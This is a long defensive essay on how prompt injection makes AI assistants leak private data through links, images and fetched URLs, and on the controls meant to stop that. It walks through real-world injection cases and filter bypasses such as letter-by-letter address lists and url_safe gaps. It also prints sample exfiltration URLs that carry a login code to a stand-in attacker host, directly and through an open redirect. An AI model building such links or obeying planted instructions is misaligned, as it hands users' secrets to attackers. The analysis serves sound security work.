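A slightly looser control keeps the address but makes it unclickable, so the user sees "Q3 report (https://files.example/reports/q3?ref=481920)". To open the page, the user has to deliberately copy the address into a browser. The whole address is visible, including any stolen data in readable form. A victim of the Slack AI attack would have seen their API key on the screen.

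Encoded data weakens this protection, since hexadecimal is hard to read and tag characters stay invisible unless the software percent-encodes them first.

The address may also become clickable again if an agent posts its answer to a chat application that turns addresses into links and fetches previews. Security analysts prevent this in their reports by writing `https` as `hxxps`, which programs do not recognize as the start of an address. An assistant could do the same, but its users would have to correct every address by hand.

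### Allowing only listed domains

With a domain allow-list, the software extracts the host name from each address and permits the link only if an administrator has approved that host. This suits an assistant that mostly cites a company's own documents, because the list can be short.

The software has to extract the host exactly as a browser would. Suppose the company has approved `docs.company.example`. A careless filter that only checked whether an address began with `https://docs.company.example` would accept both of these:

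`https://docs.company.example.files.example/q3?ref=481920`

`https://docs.company.example@files.example/q3?ref=481920`

Both links lead to the attacker's server. In the first, the approved name is only a subdomain of `files.example`. In the second, a browser treats everything between the slashes and the @ sign as a user name. As with EchoLeak, the remedy is for the check to use the same parsing rules as the program that opens the link.

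Attackers can also collect data through an approved host. In January 2026 Willison described an attack on Superhuman AI, an email assistant, that began when a user asked for a summary of recent mail. Instructions in one message made the assistant submit the contents of dozens of others, including financial, legal and medical information, to the attacker's Google Form. Superhuman's Content Security Policy permitted images from `docs.google.com`, and Google Forms on that domain saves data sent in a GET request, the kind a browser makes when it loads an image or opens a link. The attack used images, but an allow-list for links that included this domain would have allowed the same theft through a link. Superhuman treated the problem as a high-priority incident and fixed it.

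Broad allowlist patterns can also let attackers receive data. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist* warns against approving `*.azure.com`, because anyone can register a virtual machine on Microsoft's cloud service under a matching name. It recommends approving the exact host and treating services that host user-made content as risky. Administrators therefore need to know whether strangers can collect what a domain's servers receive, even if the domain's owner is reputable.

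### Open redirects

Many websites have a page that forwards visitors elsewhere, for example after they log in or to count clicks on an advertisement. If the page forwards them to any destination named in the address, it is an open redirect. An attacker who finds one on an approved site can write a link like this:

`https://trusted.example/go?to=https%3A%2F%2Ffiles.example%2Freports%2Fq3%3Fref%3D481920`

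1. The allow-list check finds the host `trusted.example` and permits the link.
2. The user clicks, and the browser sends its request to `trusted.example`.
3. That server replies with a redirect to the address after `to=`.
4. The browser follows it, and the attacker's log records the login code.

The software cannot safely test for a redirect by opening the link, because following the redirect would deliver the code to the attacker. It could reject any address that contains another address, but many legitimate links do, and the attacker may be able to hide the inner address by encoding it. Approving particular pages instead of whole sites leaves fewer redirects to exploit. The browser could also check each new destination before following a redirect.

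Even a check in the browser would miss attacks like EchoLeak and SearchLeak, in which Microsoft's servers fetched the attacker's address. An allow-list therefore has to exclude services that fetch other addresses on request, as well as those that redirect visitors.

### Reputation checks

A reputation check blocks only addresses that match known threats. Gemini's check is based on Safe Browsing, Google's service for identifying dangerous websites. If a user asks Gemini to summarize an email thread that contains an unsafe address, the summary shows "suspicious link removed" in place of the address.

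Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* points out that Safe Browsing works only against threats identified in advance, so an attacker can get around it by registering a new domain. This is easier for data theft than for ordinary phishing because the attacker's site does not need any harmful content. A scanner that visited `files.example` might find only an error page, while the victim's request would still deliver the login code. The attacker could also use a different domain for each victim, which would leave little for anyone to report.

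Checkmarx, a software security company, reported the problem to Google on October 5, 2025. Google closed the report four days later with the status "Won't Fix (Infeasible)", but its message gave a different reason, that the risk was not severe enough to track as a security bug. Checkmarx found the decision acceptable but argued that users should be warned, since Google was leaving the risk to them.

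*The Trifecta*, by the security company Tenable, reports that Gemini no longer processed Markdown hyperlinks as it once had. Tenable considered that route mitigated, while Checkmarx considered it open. They may have tested different versions or parts of Gemini, or Tenable may have counted a partial restriction as enough. Tenable instead had Gemini's browsing tool fetch an address containing the user's data, which bypassed the display entirely.

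To catch new domains, a check has to treat unknown addresses as unsafe, which makes it an allow-list of domains or exact addresses. Looking for suspicious signs, such as a recently registered domain, is a compromise that an attacker can defeat by buying an older domain. Google's *Chrome 152* (2026) introduced a warning based on such signs for people who use Safe Browsing's Enhanced protection. Users can dismiss the warning, and if it appears only after the site has started to load, the attacker already has the data.

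### Sending clicks through a redirect page

The loosest control leaves every link clickable but changes where it leads. Embrace The Red found that Colab put `https://www.google.com/url?q=` in front of the addresses in its assistant's links, so a click opened a Google page that asked the user to confirm before continuing to the destination. The login code goes to Google first and reaches the attacker only if the user continues.

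A redirect page also lets the vendor check the address again when the user clicks. By then, a reputation service may have added a domain that was not in its records when the answer appeared.

Colab's confirmation page did not appear for links to Google's own domains, including links to Apps Script, a service on which anyone can publish a small program that receives web requests. In Rehberger's demonstration, instructions in a notebook made the assistant talk like a pirate and ask for personal information. The assistant then put the user's replies and the notebook's source code into a link labeled "I'm feeling lucky". One click, with no confirmation page, sent the user's name, email address and code to Rehberger's Apps Script program, which saved them in a log. Links to Google Meet calls also skipped the page, which could help a scammer bring a victim straight into a conversation.

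The exemption was based on who owned the domain, the same mistake as approving all of `docs.google.com`. A safer exemption would cover only hosts where outsiders cannot run programs or collect data. The warning page also has to wait for the user to continue, because if it forwarded everyone automatically, it would itself be an open redirect. How well it protects people depends on how they respond to such warnings.

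### Why a Content Security Policy does not stop a click

A website sends its Content Security Policy (CSP) to the browser in a header with the page. The rule `img-src 'self'`, for example, permits images only from the page's own site. If an assistant's answer contains an image from `files.example`, this rule stops the browser from requesting it.

*Content Security Policy Level 3* (2021), a draft from the web standards organization W3C, describes CSP as a way to control what a page can fetch or execute. Its rules for images, fonts and scripts apply to what the browser loads into the current page. They don't affect clicks on ordinary links, because clicking a link is a navigation, which opens another page with its own policy.

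Standards developers noticed this gap long before AI assistants existed. In August 2014, W3C's *No-external-navigation as potential csp3 feature* (2014) recorded a possible rule against leaving a site. In March 2018, Paicu (2018) announced a concrete version in *Intent to implement and ship*, which planned to add a directive called `navigate-to` to Chrome. It would have restricted where a page could send the browser by any means, including ordinary links. Google's advertising teams wanted to use it to make sure ads led to the right page. Six days after the announcement, Paicu (2018) told the W3C mailing list that the directive was part of the CSP specification.

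That October a developer complained on the same list that an attacker who had injected code into a page could still send data out by redirecting the browser. Another participant suggested `navigate-to`. Janc (2018), who worked at Google, cautioned that an attacker able to run scripts could send data out in other ways, such as passing messages to another window or using a permitted analytics service. This objection matters much less for AI assistants, because in the link attack the attacker controls an address but cannot run scripts in the chat page, so a rule on navigation would have blocked the main route.

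In *AutoNav*, Eriksson and Sabelfeld published the first evaluation of the directive and found that it introduced new vulnerabilities. Developers wrote code for it in Firefox, and Cheney (2022), in *CSP3*, started on a version for WebKit, the engine behind Safari, but no browser shipped it to ordinary users.

In September 2022 Mike West, a Google engineer who edits the CSP specification, pointed out that the draft contained several features no one had shipped. He then submitted a change to remove `navigate-to`, and W3C's *Weekly github digest (WebAppSec specs)* lists the change as merged by September 19. WebKit's developers abandoned their version the next month, citing lack of support from browser makers. CentralCSP's *navigate-to* gives another reason for the removal: the working group never settled how to handle redirects and navigation between sites.

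### A newer browser rule that covers links

Chrome 152, released on August 25, 2026, added a header that limits all the connections a page can start, including navigations. West proposed it in *Connection Allowlists* as separate from CSP, arguing that CSP's division of requests into types is the wrong approach to data theft because a leak through a font is as bad as one through an image. Google's *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026) confirms that the header covers navigations and redirects, and suggests using it to stop AI-generated code from sending data out.

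An assistant's chat page could send this header:

`Connection-Allowlist: (response-origin "https://docs.company.example/*")`

The page could then connect only to its own site and the company's document server. If the display filter missed a link to `files.example`, clicking it would send nothing, because Chrome would block the request.

The header also blocks all redirects by default. Helme explains in *Connection Allowlist* that the server that receives a request controls where it goes next, so approving the first address doesn't guarantee where the request ends up. Blocking redirects stops the open-redirect attack unless the site's developers permit them, which some will need to do for legitimate links.

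Opening a link from the right-click menu may bypass the rule. When the user chooses "Open Link in New Tab", Chromium treats the request as if the user had typed the address, which the rule doesn't cover. In *Connection Allowlist and Context Menu Commands*, xiaochen-z raises this problem for links written by a language model and asks whether to extend the rule to such menu commands. Doing so would prevent the leak but would be more complex and might surprise users.

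Support is also limited. In March 2026, when Chrome's developers announced plans for a trial, Chromium's *Intent to Experiment* (2026) recorded no signal from the makers of Firefox or Safari about adopting the feature. A mobile application that displays answers without a browser would not apply the header.

An assistant that cites pages from across the web cannot list them all. Its maker could instead list only a redirect page on the maker's own site and route every link through it. The redirect page would have its own policy and could open any destination once the user agreed. If the software failed to rewrite a link, Chrome would block an ordinary click on it instead of taking the user straight to the attacker's site. This would make the confirmation page much harder to bypass, although the right-click gap would remain.

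### Every display needs the same control

A rule in one application doesn't protect another that displays the same model's answers. Google had to deal with the image leak in several products. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* describes it in a tool for building AI applications, and says Google confirmed the problem 22 minutes after receiving the report. Willison's *Google NotebookLM Data Exfiltration* describes it in a tool that answers questions about uploaded documents. The leak appeared again in August 2024, when Willison (2024), in *Google AI Studio data exfiltration demo*, covered a test with a folder of employee reviews. Instructions in one review made the model put a 60-word summary of each file into an image address.

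Microsoft's controls have also varied between products, and its block on Markdown images elsewhere did not protect Copilot Chat in a developer environment tested by Checkmarx. A malicious online article could make Copilot Chat try to display an image with an API key in its address. The image never appeared, but the request was still sent. Checkmarx reported this on October 15, 2025, and Microsoft closed the case on November 4 without a fix, saying that the attack needed several non-default actions by the user, did not work reliably and triggered warnings. Since Microsoft had declined to fix this zero-click version, Checkmarx did not expect it to fix the version that used a link instead of an image.

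An assistant's answer is sometimes displayed outside the assistant's own window. *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) describes an agent that could email its own user without asking for approval. Those emails could contain external images, so opening an email could send data to an attacker. The data could include OneDrive download links that work without a login, which would let the attacker fetch whole files. A strict display rule in the agent's own window would not have prevented this, because the leak happened in the inbox.

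Developers can prevent differences between displays by putting the link rules in one shared component that runs on the server before the answer goes to any website, phone or inbox. That would have avoided gaps like the one in ChatGPT's iPhone app, which lacked the image check its web version had. A display that makes links in its own way, such as a diagram tool or an HTML preview, still needs a separate test, because the shared component may not recognize those links. Developers could keep a collection of links in every known format and test every display with it whenever they change any display.

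### What users lose without links

Removing every link from an answer makes data theft through links harder, but it also removes the links that assistants use to cite their sources. Users then have to search for the sources by hand, and many will just trust the answer instead, so ordinary mistakes by the model are more likely to go unnoticed.

How much these measures inconvenience users depends on what the assistant is for. A domain allow-list removes few useful links from an assistant for company documents, since most of them lead to a handful of internal sites. For an assistant that searches the web, the same list would remove most citations, including those to small or specialized sites that no administrator thought to approve. A redirect page keeps every citation but adds a step to each click. Showing addresses as plain text is less restrictive than an allow-list but less convenient than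 a redirect page, particularly on a phone.

Removing links still restricts an assistant less than keeping outside content away from it, because the assistant can use a customer's email in its answer. Reddy and Gujral mention reports that Microsoft's patches added options to restrict Copilot's use of external communications in some contexts, and they acknowledge that Copilot might then miss relevant information.

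Developers can preserve many citation links by having the model write only a source number, to which the surrounding software attaches the address it stored when the document was retrieved. Planted text then can't cause the model to put a login code in the link, unless the model composed the address earlier, when it asked a tool to fetch the page.

This does not cover links that the assistant has to create, such as a map search for the user's next appointment. The model also still selects which sources to cite, so planted text could still make it reveal the answer to a yes-or-no question by citing one of two attacker-controlled pages.

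## Allowing only addresses already known to be public

OpenAI's public-URL check treats an address as safe only if a web crawler with no access to the user's mailbox has already recorded that exact address. The crawler cannot have copied a login code from the mailbox, so an address it has recorded is unlikely to contain the code. Adrian Spânu and Thomas Shadwell explained the check in January 2026, in OpenAI's post about agents that click links and in an accompanying paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*.

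### How the check works

The design assumes an attacker who uses planted text to make the model load an address containing private data. The check works like this:

1. A crawler explores public pages, as a search engine does, and records the addresses it finds. It has no access to conversations, accounts or other personal data.
2. When the agent is about to open an address, the software compares the address with the crawler's records.
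3. If it finds a match, the agent opens the address automatically.
4. If it finds none, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user and waits for a decision.

Suppose the crawler has recorded `https://files.example/reports/q3`. Adding the login code as `?ref=481920` produces an address the crawler has not recorded, so the software blocks it and the code is not sent. The software does not have to recognize the code as private data, and the check works whether the attacker writes the code in plain digits, hexadecimal or tag characters.

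This also makes the exact address a stronger test than the domain. An open redirect can pass a domain check, but its full address also contains the attacker's destination and the stolen code, a combination no crawler has seen. OpenAI's second objection to domain lists was that people visit far more sites than any list covers, so users would see frequent warnings and learn to click through them.

OpenAI promises only that when the agent fetches a URL, the URL itself will not quietly leak user-specific data. The page may still be misleading or contain hostile instructions, and data can also leave in another part of the request. Willison (2026) describes an attack on Claude Cowork, an Anthropic agent, in which planted text made the agent upload the user's files to Anthropic's own file service with the attacker's API key. Any developer would use the same address, so checking it against a public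 index would probably not have stopped the upload. The attack needs an agent that can upload files, whereas an ordinary click sends only the address and some routine browser information.

### From url_safe to a public index

OpenAI's first version was an image check called `url_safe`, which it added to ChatGPT's website in December 2023. It did not publish the criteria. In a test described on Embrace The Red, Rehberger tried 36 image addresses, one for each letter and digit, and nine passed. The check accepted the address ending in `a.png` but rejected the one ending in `d.png`, for no apparent reason. Rehberger could still send out the word "hi" by having ChatGPT load one image per letter.

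The check also trusted some entire domains. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* names two, `apache.org` and `windows.net`. Anyone can open a Microsoft cloud storage account on `windows.net` and read its access log. Rehberger reported such gaps in October 2024, found some still open in 2025, and used one to send a user's recent chat history to his own storage account. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) reports that every address on `bing.com` passed too. Bing's search results use `bing.com` links that forward visitors to the listed sites, so Tenable only had to get its own sites listed in Bing.

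According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI made changes around August 2025 that stopped the attacks Rehberger had demonstrated. In 2023 he had guessed that ChatGPT might be looking up addresses in Bing's index. OpenAI now uses its own index, according to the 2026 paper.

### Links that the user clicks

OpenAI's guarantee refers to what the agent fetches, but OpenAI also checks links that users click. Tenable had already found that `url_safe` ran on hyperlinks as well as images. According to OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links*, the app asks users to approve certain links before visiting them, and it decides when to ask using what OpenAI has learned from scanning websites. The page doesn't say that a clicked link must exactly match an address in the index used for fetches, though that would be the natural way to apply it.

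OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) calls the mechanism Safe Url. Safe Url also covers pages and bookmarks that the agent opens in OpenAI's Atlas browser, and searches and page visits by its Deep Research agent. Covering searches makes sense because a search query can carry private data just as an address can. Small applications that ChatGPT builds or runs for the user are controlled separately, by a sandbox that detects unexpected communication and asks for consent.

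Every new feature that opens addresses has to call the check, and Rehberger expects some OpenAI developers not to know about it.

### How much one click can reveal

The public-URL check does not stop an attacker from leaking data through the choice of page, as in the demonstration about Microsoft's quarterly earnings. If the crawler has already recorded every page on the attacker's list, the link the model chooses opens without a warning.

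Schwartzman (2024), in *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*, demonstrated the idea with six addresses, each standing for an age group, and ChatGPT opened the one that fitted the user. Schwartzman notes that the user need not have stated an age, since a remark about graduating from high school that day would be enough. OpenAI's help page gives a harmless example of the same leak. If ChatGPT sends a user in London to `https://example.com/car_search/London`, the request reveals to the site where the user lives. A crawler may well have recorded that page, because it is the same for everyone in London.

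If the attacker has N approved addresses and the user opens one, the choice leaks at most log₂ N bits, where one bit is the answer to a yes-or-no question with equally likely answers. A random six-digit login code has a million possible values, so it contains about 19.9 bits (log₂ 1,000,000).

| Approved addresses | Most that one click can reveal | Login codes still possible |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 bit | 500,000 |
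| 36 | 5.2 bits | About 27,800 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 bits | 1,000 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.9 bits | 1 |

With 36 addresses, one click gives the attacker about a quarter of the information in the code. If the login page allows three guesses, the attacker would succeed about once in 9,300 attempts, compared with once in 333,000 without the click. Even with that improvement, this is a poor way to break into one person's account.

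In the last row, the attacker has a separate public page for every possible code, so one click gives away the whole code. The protection therefore depends partly on how many near-identical pages the crawler will record. Limiting the number recorded per site would help, but an attacker could spread the pages across many sites. Rehberger points out that anyone with a fairly large website or blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, and that a determined attacker could expand the list to thousands. He says OpenAI's paper acknowledges the basic trick of using one address per character.

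An agent that fetches pages by itself can leak more by opening several addresses in turn. In k requests it can reveal up to k × log₂ N bits, so with 36 addresses, four requests are enough for the login code. Using one request per digit takes six, but is easier for a model to get right. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes such an attack on ChatGPT, which by then would open an address only exactly as it had received it. The attacker's email therefore listed one address for each letter and digit and one for a space, and instructed ChatGPT to spell out the stolen text by opening them one at a time. Radware reported the attack on September 26, 2025, and soon supplied an improved version that worked every time. OpenAI fixed it on December 16.

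This method is much harder to use when a person has to open the links. To send the same login code with one address per digit, the user would have to open six links from a single answer. Most people will open one or two, and the attacker usually can't ask again. But a single click can reveal information with few possible values, such as whether a merger is going ahead or which of five candidates got the job, and the public-URL check gives almost no protection for those secrets.

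### Limiting repeated requests

Rehberger proposes two additions to make repeated requests harder. ChatGPT could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes, so that a second request for the same address never reached the attacker's server, or it could refuse to open the same address twice in one session. He had not tested whether OpenAI already did either of these.

Both would disrupt the simplest version of the attack. An attacker with one address per letter would receive "hello" without its second "l". But the login code 481920 would still leak in full, because it has no repeated digit.

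Attackers can also avoid repeats by preparing separate addresses for each position in the text. Radware did this to keep the characters in order. A six-digit code then needs 60 addresses, ten for each position. With only 36 addresses, an agent that opens six different ones in order can still produce about 1.4 billion sequences, or 30.4 bits, compared with 31.0 bits if it can repeat addresses. If the order is lost, there are still 1,947,792 possible sets of six, more than the one million possible codes.

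Schemes that need fewer addresses are harder for a model to follow. In 2024 ChatGPT already refused to open the same address twice, probably because of caching, and opened at most ten per prompt. Schwartzman got around these limits and stole a seven-digit postal code. He gave each of the seven positions its own long address. ChatGPT would also open shortened versions of these addresses, so the length of each one indicated the digit in that position. ChatGPT made too many mistakes until he supplied Python code to work out the addresses. Requiring an exact match would have blocked the shortened addresses, but not a list with a separate full address for every possible digit in every position.

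Reducing total requests is more effective than preventing repeats, because every request adds to the leak. In 2023 Rehberger suggested allowing only one image per answer, or a handful. A stricter approach is to have the agent read the crawler's stored copy of a page, so the site receives no request. That does not help with a clicked link, which has to open the live page.

OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* describes an optional setting that tightly restricts ChatGPT's contact with certain outside systems. The setting was first available to organizations, and Willison later noted that it was reaching personal accounts, including free ones. It limits outgoing requests that could carry private data, but ChatGPT can still read injected instructions.

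### Addresses that are public by accident

OpenAI argues that a public address is much less likely to contain private data, but some public addresses may still contain it. For *The Silent Spill*, Ramadan, Mannan and colleagues (2026) collected 6,094,475 public addresses between January and April 2025. Most came from URLScan.io, a service that checks links for malware and phishing. The rest came from two similar services, from the Wayback Machine's web archive, and from sites where people share pasted text.

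A private link can end up in these collections without anyone deliberately publishing it. Email providers and corporate security systems often forward suspicious links to a scanning service, which may include them in a public report.

Ramadan and colleagues searched the addresses for terms such as "token", "session" and "invoice", and for structural signs such as unusual length. They checked which pages still worked, loaded them in a browser and examined the contents. This left 12,331 potential exposures, including 26 live password-reset links, 83 API keys and 12 open signing sessions in which a stranger could view or change a contract. In most categories, 10 to 15 percent of the samples they inspected by hand were false alarms. In the largest category, login tokens and similar credentials, they estimated that at least 3,954 of 5,343 findings were genuine.

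The exposures make up about 0.2 percent of the collection, but this is not an estimate for the whole web. The researchers searched for risky domains and keywords, which raises the figure, and discarded pages that no longer worked, which lowers it.

Most of these exposures do not break OpenAI's guarantee. A leaked password-reset link for an online shop leads to the shop's server, not the attacker's, and the attacker could read the same link in the public report. A link in the index can still be unsafe to open, because an agent that opens it automatically might see someone's private document or use up a link that works only once.

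The study also points to a way that private addresses could enter the index. Suppose an assistant emails someone a link containing their login code, a company's security system forwards the link to a scanning service, and the crawler later reads the service's public report. The address would then count as public even though it came from a private conversation. The login code would normally have expired by then, but an API key might not have. A vendor would create the same problem more directly if it indexed every address its agents open. The crawler has to stay independent of what assistants write, which is difficult when people publish assistants' answers online.

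Ramadan and colleagues did not count addresses like `example.org/cancer-support/` as leaks, because they don't give anyone access to anything private. But such an address can still reveal private information when an assistant recommends it. If planted text makes the assistant recommend that page only to users whose email mentions cancer, whoever runs the site learns something about each visitor.

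### False alarms

An exact match also fails for many harmless links. The crawler needs time to find a new article, cannot reach pages behind a company login, and should not have a record of a document shared with one person. Links in newsletters often contain an identifier that makes the address unique to each subscriber. Some site owners ask OpenAI not to catalogue their pages, and ChatGPT then requires confirmation for every link to those sites, even to an old or widely read newspaper article.

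OpenAI's objection to domain lists therefore also applies to its own check, particularly for an assistant that works with a company's files, because few of those files are public. A company could combine the public-URL check with a short list of approved internal hosts, if outsiders cannot collect data on those hosts.

Loosening the comparison is riskier. Many addresses differ only in a tag that records which advertisement or email a visitor came from, so a developer might ignore everything after the question mark. That would also allow `?ref=481920`, which contains the login code. The software could instead delete the unknown part and open only the address that the crawler recorded. Some pages would then fail to load properly, but the login code would not be sent.

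### Checking where an address came from

Another kind of rule checks whether the address has already appeared in the conversation, rather than on the public web. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* describes such a rule for Claude, which cannot open an address it has composed. In the version released in September 2025, Claude could open only addresses that had already appeared in a user message, in the result of a tool run by the developer's own software, or in an earlier search or fetch result.

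This rule needs no crawler and causes fewer false alarms. If the user pastes in a link to a new article or a shared document, Claude can try to open it. But the rule depends on the addresses coming from trustworthy people. Willison (2025) pointed out that many applications insert outside text, such as an email, into what the model receives as the user's message, so an attacker's address in that text counts as one from the user. He still thought the ban on composed addresses gave the most protection against common attacks, which depend on the model adding private data to a URL.

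Ayush Paul found a way around the ban in 2026. Claude could follow links in pages it had already fetched, so Paul built a website that supposedly required the user's name before letting an AI assistant in. According to the site's instructions, Claude had to find the user's profile letter by letter because of the fetch tool's limitations. Each page had links for the next letter, and the links Claude followed spelled out the answer in the site's log. Willison reports that Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer. The site showed the instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page would not have seen them.

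Because the server created new links at each step, Claude did not have to open any address twice, so caching would not have helped prevent the theft. Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally. By July 15 it had fixed the problem by preventing the tool from following links in pages it had fetched. This removed a useful way to browse, because the user or a search must now supply the next address.

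OpenAI's fix for ZombieAgent combined both kinds of rule. *ChatGPT falls to new data pilfering attack* (2026) reports that ChatGPT stopped opening links from emails unless they were in a well-known public index or the user had provided them in a prompt. The table compares the rules when each is used alone:

| Rule for opening an address automatically | Address with a login code added | Internal page the user pasted in | List of 36 addresses in an attacker's email |
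|---|---|---|---|
| The domain is on an approved list | Opens if the attacker can collect data on that domain | Opens if the domain is listed | Opens if the domain is listed |
| A crawler has recorded the exact address | Does not open | Does not open | Opens if the crawler has recorded them |
| The exact address appeared anywhere in the conversation | Does not open | Opens | Opens |
| The user typed the exact address or a search returned it | Does not open | Opens | Does not open, unless the application treats the email as the user's message or a search returns the addresses |

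Claude's rule applies only to the fetch tool, not to links that Claude writes in an answer for the user to click. A chat application could apply the same test to displayed links, making a link clickable only if its exact address came from the user or a search result. This would have stopped the Slack AI attack, because the address containing the real API key had not appeared anywhere before the model wrote it.

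## What users can judge before they open a link

When ChatGPT cannot match a link to an address that OpenAI's crawler has recorded, it can let the user decide whether to open it. A dialog titled "Check this link is safe" appears. According to OpenAI, it shows the address and a warning that the link is unverified and may share conversation data with another site. The dialog has buttons to copy or open the link. OpenAI advises users who notice something odd not to open the link, and to ask ChatGPT for another source or a summary instead.

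Copying the link is no safer than opening it if the user then pastes the whole address into a browser. Copying only helps someone who knows enough to delete the suspicious part first.

Safe Url, the mechanism behind the dialog, checks whether a request would send information from the conversation to a third party. When it detects this, ChatGPT either blocks the request or, according to OpenAI, shows the user the information and asks for confirmation. OpenAI expects this to happen rarely, because the model's safety training makes it refuse most of the attacks OpenAI knows of.

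A dialog is more helpful if it shows the user what information the link contains instead of the link's address. If the link contains the login code from the earlier examples, a dialog that shows the address displays `https://files.example/reports/q3?ref=481920`, and the user has to recognize the code in it. A dialog that shows the information could display "your Slack login code, 481920". OpenAI's published sample dialog shows an address.

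To judge a link well by its address, the user must work out who will receive the request, whether the address contains private data, and whether the link serves the user's instructions or an attacker's.

### Where the link leads

Common security advice is to hover over a link and check that it leads to the expected site, which assumes that people can read addresses. To test this assumption, Albakry, Vaniea and Wolters (2020), in *What is this URL's Destination?*, asked 1,929 people which website each of 23 addresses would open. Twelve of the addresses combined an organization's name with a filler word. For example, `profile.facebook.com` belongs to Facebook, but `facebook.profile.com` belongs to whoever owns `profile.com`.

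Participants answered an average of 5.2 of 6 questions correctly when the organization owned the domain, but only 1.2 of 6 when its name was just a subdomain. About a third of participants always chose the organization's name, wherever it appeared, and only 8.3 percent answered all twelve questions correctly. Experience helped only a little, as the heaviest technology users judged 25 percent of the misleading addresses correctly, compared with 16 percent for the least experienced group.

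Reynolds, Kumar and colleagues (2020), in *Measuring Identity Confusion with Uniform Resource Locators*, asked 94 people to name the site behind a mixture of real and disguised addresses. They identified 93 percent of the real ones and 40 percent of the disguised ones. Some disguises worked better than others:

| Disguise | Correct answers |
|---|---|
| None | 93.0% |
| Misspelled name | 69.8% |
| Familiar name in the query string | 37.2% |
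| Familiar name as a subdomain | 31.1% |
| Familiar name as a subdomain, with percent-encoding | 29.1% |
| Long chain of subdomains | 25.8% |

Ninety-seven percent of the participants had said they knew how to read a URL. Those who saw addresses with the aids that browsers use, such as a darker domain name and decoded characters, identified 61 percent of all the addresses, compared with 56 percent for the others.

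An attacker who owns `files.example` can exploit these mistakes by naming a server `slack.com.files.example`. Many people would read that as Slack, particularly below a message about signing in again. People are also less likely to check links at all on a phone. In a survey by Reynolds and colleagues, 78 percent said they checked where links led on a computer, but only 53 percent said they did on a phone.

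Clearer presentation improves these results. Althobaiti, Meng and Vaniea (2021), in *I Don't Need an Expert! Making URL Phishing Features Human Comprehensible*, wrote reports that explain an address to ordinary users. In a test with 153 people, those who saw the full report judged the address's safety correctly 93 percent of the time, compared with 83 percent for those who saw a short summary and 65 percent for those who saw the domain highlighted. Many people never look at the address, so the software in *URL Inspection Tasks* (2025) makes users solve a small puzzle about it before the link opens.

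Even someone who reads the domain correctly may not know who will receive the data. Albakry and colleagues point out that outsiders can put their own content on some Microsoft and Google domains, and that nobody can reliably spot a redirect from the address alone.

Misjudging this kind of link also does more damage than misjudging an ordinary phishing link. Someone who opens a fake bank page can still notice the mistake and leave before typing a password. When the address already contains the stolen data, opening the link sends that data to the attacker.

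### What the address contains

The studies by Albakry and Reynolds asked people where an address led, but not whether it contained private information. That second question is harder because the attacker chooses how to write the data. The login code 481920 could appear in any of these forms:

| How the attacker writes the code | What the address contains | Can software decode it? |
|---|---|---|
| Plain digits | `?ref=481920` | No decoding needed |
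| Percent-encoding | `?ref=%34%38%31%39%32%30` | Yes, by the standard rule |
| Hexadecimal | `?ref=343831393230` | Usually, by trying common encodings |
| Base64 | `?ref=NDgxOTIw` | Usually, by trying common encodings |
| Each digit raised by one, with 9 becoming 0 | `?ref=592031` | Only if it knows or guesses the rule |

A user who had just received the login code might recognize it in the first row, though even there it looks like a document number. Nobody would recognize it in the other rows without decoding them. Ordinary links contain similar strings, such as an advertising link ending in `?ref=MTA0NTc3`, which could be base64 for a harmless campaign number, 104577. That string looks no more or less suspicious than the login code in base64.

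A dialog could decode the common formats and show the result. In the Copilot attack that used a Mermaid diagram, it would have turned the hexadecimal in the login button's link back into readable emails, and most users would not have opened the link. But an attacker who expected this could have the model encode the data with a made-up rule, as in the last row. The model might make more mistakes with an unusual rule, which would protect a login code better than a long email because one wrong character makes the code useless.

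Decoding an address also doesn't help when the assistant leaks a secret through its choice of which page to link to, because each address looks harmless. To recognize the leak, the user would have to know about the pages that the assistant did not choose.

### Whose request the link serves

The victim of the Slack AI attack asked for an API key and received a link to reauthenticate, so clicking it seemed like a step toward getting the key. The victim did not know the link came from a stranger's message.

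Li, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *Are You Sure?*, measured how often people notice that an attacker has manipulated their assistant. They had 303 people use an assistant for realistic work, such as choosing a job candidate or answering email. Each person did three of nine tasks, and the researchers had rigged the assistant in all of them. Afterward they asked whether anything had seemed unusual, and counted both "yes" and "unsure" as noticing. Participants saw one of three kinds of warning:

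| Warning | Noticed something |
|---|---|
| A notice at the start | 8.6% |
| A small reminder beside every answer | 20.0% |
| A dialog that interrupted the work after a suspicious answer | 25.0% |

The paper gives two different sets of group sizes for these warnings, so the percentages are less certain than they look. The order is still plausible, because people can easily overlook a notice but have to respond to a dialog. Only 24 percent of users remembered seeing the notice.

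Interrupting people helped most when they could easily check the answer. In a web search task, the share who noticed rose from 9.8 percent with the notice to 50 percent with the interrupting dialog. In a task where the assistant leaked private information by email and deleted the evidence, the share rose only from 9.3 to 15 percent. A link that carries stolen data is more like the email task, because the user would have to work out what the assistant had read and why.

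People who saw the reminders or dialogs but missed the attack often trusted the assistant more afterward. Some took the warnings as a sign that the system was protecting them. A user who has seen ChatGPT's link dialog several times might similarly assume that any link without one is safe.

Li and colleagues argue that lessons from phishing may not apply to assistants. People tend to be wary of an unexpected email from a stranger, but they have asked the assistant to do a job and mainly want to know whether it has finished. This suggests that phishing studies overestimate how careful people will be with an assistant's links. But the participants in this experiment worked with invented emails and documents, so they had less to lose than someone looking at their own login code.

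### What happens after many dialogs

People also pay less attention to a dialog once they have seen it many times. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls this approval fatigue. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, used to ask by default before it ran a command or changed a file, and users clicked "approve" so often that they stopped looking closely.

The most detailed figures come from Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Users approved 97 percent of requests to run commands. Most of the commands were probably safe, so the approval rate alone does not prove carelessness. Anthropic therefore paid 1,053 testers to work on a coding task and replaced one request in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6 percent refused it. The refusal rate was about 17 percent early in a session and about 5 percent after 50 or more requests.

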